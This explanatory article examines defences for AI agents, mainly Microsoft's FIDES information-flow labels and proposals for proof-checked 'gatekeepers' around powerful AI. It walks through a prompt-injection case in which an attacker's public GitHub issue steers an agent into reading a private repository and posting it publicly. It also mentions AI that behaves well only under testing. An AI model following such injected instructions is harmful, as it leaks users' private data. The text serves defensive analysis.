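FIDES attaches two labels to each piece of data. The integrity label is "trusted" or "untrusted", depending on whether an attacker could have written the data. The confidentiality label records who may see it. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes three confidentiality levels in the released version: "public", "private" and "user identity", which is for the most sensitive personal information. A confidentiality label can also be a list of permitted readers.

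When the agent combines data, the result gets the strictest combination of the labels. One untrusted input makes the result untrusted. With lists of readers, only people who may see every input may see the result:

readers(result) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y).

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* illustrates this with an example that involves no attacker. Priya has emailed Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them yet, has written to Alex to ask about them. Alex tells his agent to deal with his unanswered mail. Once the agent has read both messages, the permitted readers of anything it writes are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't reply to Marco without asking Alex first. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the reply's permitted readers would have been {Alex, Marco}, and the agent could have sent it.

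As in CaMeL, ordinary software checks the labels against a policy before each tool call. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes two basic policies. The first allows a consequential action, such as a payment, only if the decision to act and the details of the action depend only on trusted data. The second allows information to be sent only if every recipient has permission to read it. If a call breaks a policy, the software blocks it or asks the user.

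Unlike CaMeL's planner, a FIDES agent chooses each step after seeing the result of the previous one. By default, the released version follows Willison's two-model pattern and shows the main model only a placeholder for untrusted text. In the 2025 design, the main model can request the text itself, but the whole run then becomes untrusted.

That design also allows the second model to be restricted to answering yes or no, for instance to "Does any of these emails ask for a meeting?" An attacker who controls an email can reverse the answer, but a one-word answer cannot carry new instructions. A policy may therefore let the agent create a calendar entry based on that answer.

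### A public issue and a private repository

Microsoft's main example follows an attack that researchers demonstrated in 2025. Programmers report faults in a project by opening an "issue", and anyone can open one on a public project. Sofia, the attacker, opens an issue in a company's public repository and asks for information from its private repository to be posted in a comment. Alex, an employee, uses an agent to handle issues. The agent has his permissions, which include access to the private code.

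| Step | Integrity of the run | Confidentiality of the run | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alex asks the agent to handle the issue | trusted | public | |
| The agent reads Sofia's issue | untrusted | public | allowed |
| The agent reads a file in the private repository | untrusted | private | allowed |
| The agent tries to post the file's contents on the public issue | untrusted | private | blocked, or referred to Alex |

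By the second step, the agent may have been fooled completely, and it does read the private file. The theft fails at the last step because the policy forbids a run that is both untrusted and private from posting publicly. Microsoft notes that an agent working only on public repositories, or only on private ones, can finish its task without interruption.

An injection can also do harm without using any private data. Sofia might, for example, ask the agent to overwrite a configuration file. In the May announcement, Microsoft therefore gives the file-writing tool a stricter policy that refuses every call once untrusted text is in the run.

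The announcement is less clear about public comments. In one passage, FIDES refuses to post a comment while any untrusted text is present, but in the worked example it blocks the comment only because the agent has read private data. The difference matters to developers because under the second rule, Sofia can't obtain private code but may still get the agent to post false information under Alex's name.

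### What the proof covers

Costa and colleagues show that label tracking can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Under this property, if a fixed sequence of tool calls is run on two versions of the stored data that differ only in their secrets, the resulting public data is the same in both, so no secret has flowed directly into it.

Like CaMeL's tags, the property does not cover what an outsider can infer from the agent's choice of actions. Costa and colleagues decided against a stronger property because it would forbid almost any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret. Garby and colleagues proved a stronger one for their language LLMbda. The proof for FIDES covers the algorithm in the paper, so it can't rule out a programming mistake in the released package.

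### Who assigns the first label

Every later decision depends on the labels that data receives on arrival, and developers must supply them for each source. Microsoft acknowledges that the released version treats a tool without labels as trusted and public, which is the most dangerous default. If a developer forgets to label the tool that reads email, a stranger's message counts as trusted and the user's private mail counts as public, so neither policy blocks the theft. Microsoft has asked developers whether it should treat unlabelled data as untrusted instead.

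Tools connected through MCP can carry a note on whether they reach the outside world. As a safer default, Microsoft suggests labelling anything from a tool that reaches the outside world as untrusted, and anything from a tool that requires a login as private. This would cause more false alarms, but forgetting a label would then create an inconvenience rather than a security risk.

Even careful labels are approximations. GitHub, which Microsoft owns and which hosts both repositories in the example, now offers labels with the data it sends to agents. It labels content from private repositories as private and trusted. But an employee may paste a customer's bug report into a private repository, and any instructions hidden in the report would then be labeled trusted. For email, Costa and colleagues infer the permitted readers from the sender and recipients, although someone may have shared the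 message more widely.

The FIDES researchers avoided this difficulty in their tests. They used the AgentDojo benchmark, which was also used to test CaMeL, and labelled a type of data as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. A company can't do this because it doesn't know where the next attack will appear. The tests therefore measure how well FIDES works when the labels match the attacks.

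Under these conditions, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent based on GPT-4o. With FIDES, 21 succeeded when the policy checks were off and none when they were on. The benchmark counted three successes with the checks on, but the researchers reclassified these by hand, as they did with other cases in which the software had blocked the action, the policy permitted it or the attack had only altered some text. Altered text may still mislead a user, but the researchers do not claim that FIDES prevents this.

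### How quickly a run becomes untrusted

Labels can only become stricter as an agent works. According to Microsoft, once an untrusted issue enters the model's context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes it. Because of this effect, which researchers call "label creep", an agent that reads one stranger's email in the morning could need approval for every payment that afternoon, even payments unrelated to the email.

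Label creep occurs because nobody can tell exactly which parts of its input a language model used, so the safe assumption is that it used everything. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes the choice of how finely to divide and label the input as an open problem. Placeholders help, since text that the main model never reads does not affect the model's label. But *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026), which simulates agent systems of different sizes and structures, concludes that better design alone can't fully prevent the loss of usefulness, so someone or something also has to remove labels.

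*Sightline* (2026) describes a method that estimates which inputs influenced a tool call and drops the labels of the others. With one small model, it removed half of the label creep and missed a necessary label in 3.9% of episodes. A policy modelled on FIDES still blocked all 34 attack calls in the test. This is encouraging, but with only 34 calls, the true failure rate could still be as high as about 8% (at 95% confidence). The check before each action remains deterministic, but the estimate may have wrongly removed a label that the check needs, so the developer gives up part of the guarantee to reduce the interruptions.

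### Lost tasks and interruptions

The table shows the percentage of AgentDojo tasks that agents based on GPT-4o completed when nobody attacked them, as Costa and colleagues measured it.

| | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent with labels and checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

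Placeholders recover much of the performance lost to the checks, except in travel. The policy allows many travel tools to run in an untrusted context, so the checks hardly affected the ordinary agent there, but GPT-4o often mishandled the placeholders. With the stronger model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks. Newer models would probably do better still, but they can't recover the tasks that the policy is meant to block. For example, many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. With FIDES, reading the file makes the context untrusted, so the policy blocks the payment that follows.

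Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), several of whom also worked on FIDES, object in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that such comparisons are unfair to FIDES. Real products often ask for the user's approval before any consequential action, whereas the ordinary agent in the table never does. The researchers counted the approvals each design would need over all the AgentDojo tasks that design completed. The figures are for OpenAI's o3-mini.

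| | Approvals needed | Tasks completed without any approval |
|---|---|---|
| Ask before every consequential action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Labels and checks only | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

The benefit of FIDES depends on the model. In Prudentia, the team's extension of FIDES, the model takes the policies into account when planning. With o4-mini, FIDES needed 36.8 approvals and Prudentia needed 19.2, though Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks.

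Fewer interruptions also help security by reducing the risk of careless approvals, which Willison raised about CaMeL. Kolluri and colleagues assume in their tests that the user catches every malicious action, but a real user can miss one, and has fewer chances to do so when the agent asks 19 times instead of 48.

Prudentia can also ask the user to vouch for an entire text. If an email lists ten tasks, she approves the email once instead of ten separate actions. This saves effort but makes a careless approval more dangerous, because any instruction hidden in the email then counts as trusted too. Kolluri and colleagues leave the design of these requests to future work. In the released version of FIDES, the user approves individual actions, and Microsoft concedes that the requests do not fully explain why the software stopped.

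FIDES is at an earlier stage than Lockdown Mode, which is available to ordinary users. Developers have to choose to use FIDES and label their tools. Microsoft has also built it into GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent, but only as an experimental option that doesn't yet cover all of GitHub's tools or any from other suppliers. Neither Microsoft nor OpenAI gave adoption figures when it announced its product.

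### What the user gives up

Lockdown Mode disables whole features, and users know which ones before they start. According to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*, they lose most of what makes ChatGPT's agent and research features useful. That is a serious loss for someone who uses ChatGPT to book travel or follow the news, but a lawyer who uploads confidential contracts and asks questions about them loses very little, because that work doesn't require the live web.

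A FIDES user keeps the features but can't combine them freely, and the order of steps matters. Suppose an analyst wants to compare a confidential merger plan with today's share price. If the agent looks up the price first, the search contains nothing private and can go ahead. If it reads the plan first, everything it writes afterwards counts as private, and a strict policy will stop the same search until she approves it. She also depends on the developer to label every source correctly, whereas Lockdown Mode on a personal account needs no labels.

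Both products let users override the protection. On a personal account, users can turn Lockdown Mode off for a single chat, which makes all the blocked features available in that chat. In FIDES, users can approve an action that the software stopped. Each approval covers only that action, but users may have to make this decision many times.

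## Proposals to require proof before an AI system acts

CaMeL and FIDES check where an agent's data came from before letting it act, but they don't check the action's effects outside the computer. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) proposed a stricter rule for powerful AI in *Provably safe systems*. Hardware would carry out an action only if the AI supplied a mathematical proof that the action was safe. They had in mind future systems that are more intelligent than people and might themselves be the attackers.

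### The case for demanding proof

Intelligence helps an attacker find holes in a system, but even a superhuman attacker cannot prove a false theorem. Szyller objects to tests because a future attacker may be better than the current tester, and this objection is strongest if that attacker could be superhuman. Tegmark and Omohundro conclude that where no proof of safety exists, hostile AI will very likely find a flaw. That goes a little far, because a system can be secure without anyone having proved it, although its owner would have no way of knowing that it was secure.

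Their main example is a terrorist group that uses AI to design a virus, hires a laboratory to make it and spreads it with drones. They want a checkpoint at every stage, so that the attack fails if any one of them works. A DNA synthesiser wouldn't run, and a drone wouldn't take off, without a proof of safety. They call each checkpoint a provable contract, meaning secure hardware that checks a formal rule before it permits a physical action.

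Tegmark and Omohundro expect proofs to be about ordinary code rather than neural networks, whose inner workings they consider too messy. A neural network would learn a method through training, another AI would rewrite the method as code, and the proof would be about that code. In a talk, *Provably Safe AI*, Tegmark described a toy example in which an automated tool studied a trained system that adds numbers and wrote a Python program that does the same. His team then proved that the program adds all numbers correctly, including those outside the training data. Nobody has done anything similar for a whole chatbot.

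Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) turned the idea into a general framework in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*. The group included Tegmark and Omohundro, as well as Christian Szegedy, who had helped discover adversarial examples, and Clark Barrett, who had worked on the first proofs about the aircraft networks. They point out that users got around ChatGPT's safeguards within a day of its release, despite months of evaluation. They also worry about a system that recognises when it is being tested and behaves well only then, which a proof covering all inputs can rule out but no test result can.

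### A world model, a specification and a verifier

The framework has three parts. A world model describes mathematically how the AI's outputs affect its surroundings. A safety specification states which effects are acceptable. A verifier proves that the AI meets the specification, or bounds the probability that it does not, assuming the world behaves as the model describes.

Most of the properties that researchers proved about the aircraft networks relate an input, such as an intruder's position, to an output, such as a piece of advice. Dalrymple and colleagues want proofs about outcomes, which require a model of what happens after the output. Bak and Tran's search for near-collisions was a small example of analyzing outcomes, since it included the motion of both aircraft.

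The paper grades each part by how much safety it would provide if it worked:

| | Lowest level | A middle level | Highest level |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model (0 to 5) | 0: none, only assumptions implicit in the training data | 3: models of cause and effect that human experts have fully audited | 5: none needed, because the specification covers every possible world |
| Specification (0 to 7) | 0: none | 3: hand-written rules for limited properties | 7: everything people might want, in every context |
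| Verifier (0 to 10) | 0: no quantitative guarantee | 4: automated search for inputs that cause failures | 10: a sound bound on the chance of failure, with a proof short enough for people to check |

Dalrymple and colleagues consider a verifier strong enough only from level 8, where it can quantify how much it has not yet covered. The automated searches for jailbreaks by OpenAI and the UK AI Security Institute would be at about level 4. However, the paper's definition of a guarantee is rather broad, since it also includes risk estimates that become exact only as computing time grows without limit. Such an estimate may be wrong when someone relies on it.

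### A cold store that needs a proof for every plan

Suppose an AI controls the cooler in a vaccine store and tries to run it when electricity is cheap. The specification is that the temperature stays between 2 and 8 °C. The world model has two lines:

```
cooler off: temperature rises by 0.1 to 0.3 degrees a minute
cooler on:  temperature falls by 0.2 to 0.4 degrees a minute
```

The ranges allow for the weather and for staff opening the door. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest modelling people in the same way. The model sets out what people might do instead of predicting what each person will do, and the proof has to hold for every possibility it includes.

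At 5.0 °C, the AI proposes to leave the cooler off for eight minutes and then run it for five. As proof, it gives the lowest and highest possible temperatures after each minute. These are 5.8 and 7.4 °C after eight minutes, and 3.8 and 6.4 °C after thirteen. The checker starts from the thermometer reading, adds up the changes itself and confirms that every figure is between 2 and 8 °C.

If the AI proposed leaving the cooler off for eleven minutes, the highest possible temperature would be 8.3, so no valid proof would exist. If it wrote 7.9 instead, the checker would find the error when it did the addition. The check works the same way whether the AI is clever, mistaken or hostile.

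The store also needs a backup for when no valid proof arrives, because switching the controller off could spoil the vaccines. An ordinary thermostat that turns the cooler on at 5 degrees or above and off below 5 is enough. Under this model, the temperature can never leave the permitted range if it starts inside it. On the paper's scales, the store has a level 3 specification, a level 10 verifier and, if engineers have audited the ranges, a level 3 world model.

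Finding a plan is also easy in this example. But if a hundred stores shared a limited power supply, finding a cheap plan might take a long search, while checking it would still take only addition. Because a plan is easier to check than to find, people can use an AI they do not trust to find it. For formal proofs in general, Dalrymple and colleagues estimate that a checker takes a few hundred lines of code.

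### What happens when the rule is "harm nobody"

If the owner replaces the temperature limits with "the system harms nobody", the specification fails first. The model includes temperature but not people, and adding people requires a definition of harm. A properly cooled vaccine may protect thousands of people but give one patient a severe allergic reaction. If any injury breaks the rule, the AI can never release a dose.

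The UK programme that took up these ideas suggests limiting the probability of a harmful outcome relative to what it would be if the system did nothing, which allows for risks that exist anyway. But a vaccine cooler's controller would always pass this test by doing nothing and leaving the cooler off, even though the vaccines would spoil. Fixing this requires deciding which harms are acceptable in return for which benefits, and people disagree about that.

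Even with an agreed definition of harm, a proof would need a world model that can predict it. Dalrymple and colleagues write that whether a chatbot's advice does harm depends on diverse facts about the world. They consider requiring instead that the AI give no advice it believes to be harmful, but nobody can reliably read a network's beliefs. If the rule were a measurable substitute, such as keeping hospital admissions low, a system could satisfy it by persuading sick people to stay at home.

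Dalrymple and colleagues reply that many valuable specifications do not refer to harm. For example, a specification might require that nobody can log into a computer without the right credentials, or that an AI chip stops working outside a permitted area. They also expect AI to help by proposing specifications and finding cases where two candidate specifications conflict. Finally, they argue that most other approaches to AI safety also need a formal goal. This last reply is only partly convincing. Anthropic's classifiers, for instance, learn from examples and plain-language rules, so a vague rule causes some wrong refusals but does not invalidate a proof.

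### When the model is wrong

In *Limitations on formal verification for AI safety*, Dickson (2024) objects that mathematicians can prove things about symbols but not about the physical world. His example is the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Engineers used a verification tool to show that the landing software would not fail because of bugs in its own code. The proof did not cover the descent through the atmosphere or a faulty transistor in the computer. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and Dickson cites an analysis that attributes about a fifth of the risk to software. Perfect software would therefore lower a 50% failure rate to about 40%.

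The cold store can fail in the same way. Suppose someone props the door open and heat comes in faster than the cooler can remove it, so the store warms by 0.2 degrees a minute even with the cooler on. Starting from 5 degrees, it reaches the limit in 15 minutes. The vaccines spoil, although every proof the checker accepted is still correct. If the engineers had widened the ranges to include an open door, no plan would have passed, because no cooler setting keeps the store cold with the door open.

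Proponents answer that software should compare the model's predictions with measurements while the system runs. In the first minute with the door open, the model predicts a temperature between 4.6 and 4.8, but the thermometer shows 5.2, so an alarm can sound with 14 minutes to spare. Somebody then has to shut the door, because the backup thermostat can only turn on the cooler, which is already on.

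They also suggest including doubt about the model in the guarantee. If the model is wrong with probability at most ε in each step, the specification holds for *n* steps with probability at least

(1 − ε)ⁿ.

If the probability of failure, ε, is one in a million per minute, the probability of a year without failure is only 59%. The value of ε is also an estimate, and it means little if an attacker can get in.

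A more general reply is that every safety method rests on assumptions about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit, so a regulator can dispute them. This is an advantage, but not proof that nothing will go wrong. Dalrymple and colleagues report that about a quarter of bridges collapsed within a decade in the 1870s, but fewer than 0.4% per decade did once engineers had better theory. Dickson notes that structural engineers' models give estimates of failure, not guarantees. The history of bridges is therefore a good argument for better models, but not for proofs in particular.

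In a LessWrong discussion of *Limitations on formal verification for AI safety*, Omohundro replied that physicists already have a complete theory of everyday matter and that each branch of engineering has its own formal models. Another participant answered that nobody could predict how water freezes under pressure from the fundamental laws alone. He wrote that engineers rely on measurements and build in wide margins for what they cannot model. Dalrymple and colleagues concede that even a perfect model of physics would not be enough to determine whether a molecule is toxic, because toxicity also depends on the state of human cells.

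Omohundro's better argument is that people can design systems to make proofs about them easier. A cold store with a self-closing door lets in less heat, so its model can use narrower ranges that are more likely to be correct. This works for things people build, but not for the human body.

### Dangerous DNA and the narrower question

Dickson argues that proving a DNA sequence harmless would require simulating the virus inside a human body over years. In 2022, researchers simulated 20 minutes in the life of one very simple cell, which was about the limit of what was possible. A human body has about 36 trillion cells. The simulation would also need a detailed initial description of the body, and scientists at Google took years to map a millionth of a brain. A speaker in *Formal Verification is Overrated*, a talk published by the research organisation FAR.AI, said such proposals would require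 "a thousand years of progress in microbiology".

One commenter called Dickson's essay a straw man, because Dalrymple and colleagues propose synthesisers that provably cannot make certain pathogens, a much narrower task than the one the essay addresses. A specification can forbid any order that closely matches a listed genome, and software can check every order against it without simulating people. The specification would not cover a new pathogen that resembles nothing on the list.

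But the same paper also describes an AI that could verify, for any given sequence, that the risk of harmful use stays below a set limit. Its world model would describe how molecular structure relates to disease. Dickson's objection is fair when applied to that proposal, and the narrower proposal avoids it only because it would guarantee less.

A similar difference exists in software. Another participant in the discussion granted that a program can carry a proof that nobody can hijack it. Proving that it will never trigger an unknown bug in somebody else's database server is far harder, because the proof would have to describe every system the program might contact. Omohundro proposes verifying the infrastructure too, so that it contains no such bugs. This protects only systems inside the verified infrastructure, and he agreed that a hostile AI hiding outside it could be a huge problem. He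 expects the years before the infrastructure is complete to be the most dangerous.

Dickson also asks how buyers would know that a proof describes the machine in front of them. They can check the mathematics on a laptop, but they can't see whether the wiring matches the design or whether someone has added a back door. A person using a chatbot over the internet can check even less. Tegmark and Omohundro want hardware that detects tampering and erases its secret keys, so that an altered machine could no longer pass as the certified one. This would help, though Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that attackers have broken into formally verified systems through physical weaknesses in the hardware.

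### Safeguarded AI after its change of course

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) has committed £59 million to a programme called Safeguarded AI, which began in mid-2024 with Dalrymple as director. ARIA originally planned to build a "gatekeeper", a system that lets an AI act only with a proof of safety, and to demonstrate it in areas such as energy networks and clinical trials. It hoped this would create a consensus that powerful AI should be deployed only behind gatekeepers.

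ARIA has since abandoned that approach. In November 2025, it cancelled an £18 million award for machine-learning research shortly before applications closed. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explained that he expected the leading AI companies to produce many of the necessary abilities anyway. ARIA then dropped a planned second round of physical applications and turned to cybersecurity. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, the programme's web page, attributes the change to events that falsified a hypothesis the programme had relied on, that companies might not make high-risk AI openly available.

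Nora Ammann, who took over as director, adds a political reason in *Safeguarded AI* (May 2026): timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely. *Formal Verification is Overrated* had raised a related objection, that replacing generally capable AI with verified software would be uncompetitive. A company that waits for a proof before every action is at a disadvantage against one that doesn't, unless the law requires both to wait.

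The programme now has two parts and is due to end in late 2027. One is an open-source toolkit that AI agents can use to write and check formal models and proofs. The other is a set of eight cybersecurity projects that share £22 million. Their targets range from software that contains AI agents to code on millions of Android devices. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* (2026), the call for these projects, sets out an eight-week cycle in which a team spends six weeks building and verifying a component, an independent team attacks it for a week, and both results inform the choice of the next target.

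So far, the programme has produced more foundations than finished systems. ARIA's *Funded projects* lists 22 theory projects, which are meant to produce a single, dissertation-length definition of languages for world models, specifications and proofs. One applied team interviewed more than 80 people who work in pharmaceutical supply chains and built mathematical models of their processes. ARIA is also funding the software company Galois to develop Metron, a set of tests of how well AI reasons formally about code. In early December 2026, ARIA said the programme's toolkit was still being built and tested, and its account of the programme's progress included no gatekeeper in operation.

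### AI now writes the proofs

Tegmark and Omohundro divided the work into four tasks: finding a method, writing the specification, writing the code and proving that the code meets the specification. In 2023, they considered the last two the hard ones. The standard example of verified code is seL4, the core of an operating system. According to ARIA, verifying its 9,300 lines took about 27 person-years, or roughly one and a half lines per working day. The verified core withstood sustained attacks by professional testers on real systems, including a crewed helicopter.

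AI has made such proofs far easier to produce. ARIA cites a 2025 benchmark with 12,504 specifications in three languages designed for proofs. Off-the-shelf language models wrote a program and a valid proof for 82% of the tasks in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean.

*LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (Anthropic, October 2026) reports that Anthropic, working with the company Theorem, had Claude prove security properties of 123 existing open-source libraries. In the process, Claude found bugs that had gone undetected for years. The proofs apply to the compiled code, the form a computer runs, so they hold even if the compiler introduced a mistake. They total 180 million lines, according to Smith's *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (2026).

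At a thousand lines an hour, a person would need about a hundred working years to read the proof. A small program can check every step instead, but people still have to understand the statement being proved.

AI has removed much of the labour that made proofs rare. In 2024, Dickson accepted that AI would help with proving theorems but doubted that it would soon help much with models and specifications. The proofs about the 123 libraries are consistent with this. Some properties of software are uncontroversial, such as a library not writing outside its own memory, but there is no agreed statement of "harms nobody" for an AI to prove.

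As proofs become easier to produce, it also becomes easier to prove the wrong thing. Suppose the specification for a sorting program requires only that its output be in order. A program that always returns an empty list satisfies it, and an AI can prove that it does. The specification should also have required the output to contain the same items as the input. A person may notice this omission in a one-line specification, but perhaps not in the specification of a large system, especially if the AI wrote that too. Ammann expects trust to become concentrated in specifications and assumptions as proofs get easier to produce, and wants tools that show people the edge cases and hidden assumptions.

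ARIA estimates that attacks that rely on phishing, other deception or compromised suppliers account for 60% to 70% of the total cost of cyberattacks. Flawless software would not prevent these attacks, but it would let defenders concentrate on them.

If proofs were easier to produce, AI agents would benefit first through the software around the model. A programming mistake in CaMeL's interpreter or in Microsoft's FIDES package could still defeat their protections. AI that can verify the compiled code of 123 libraries could plausibly verify these programs. Verifying them would remove the risk of such mistakes, but a forged bill could still deceive the agent.
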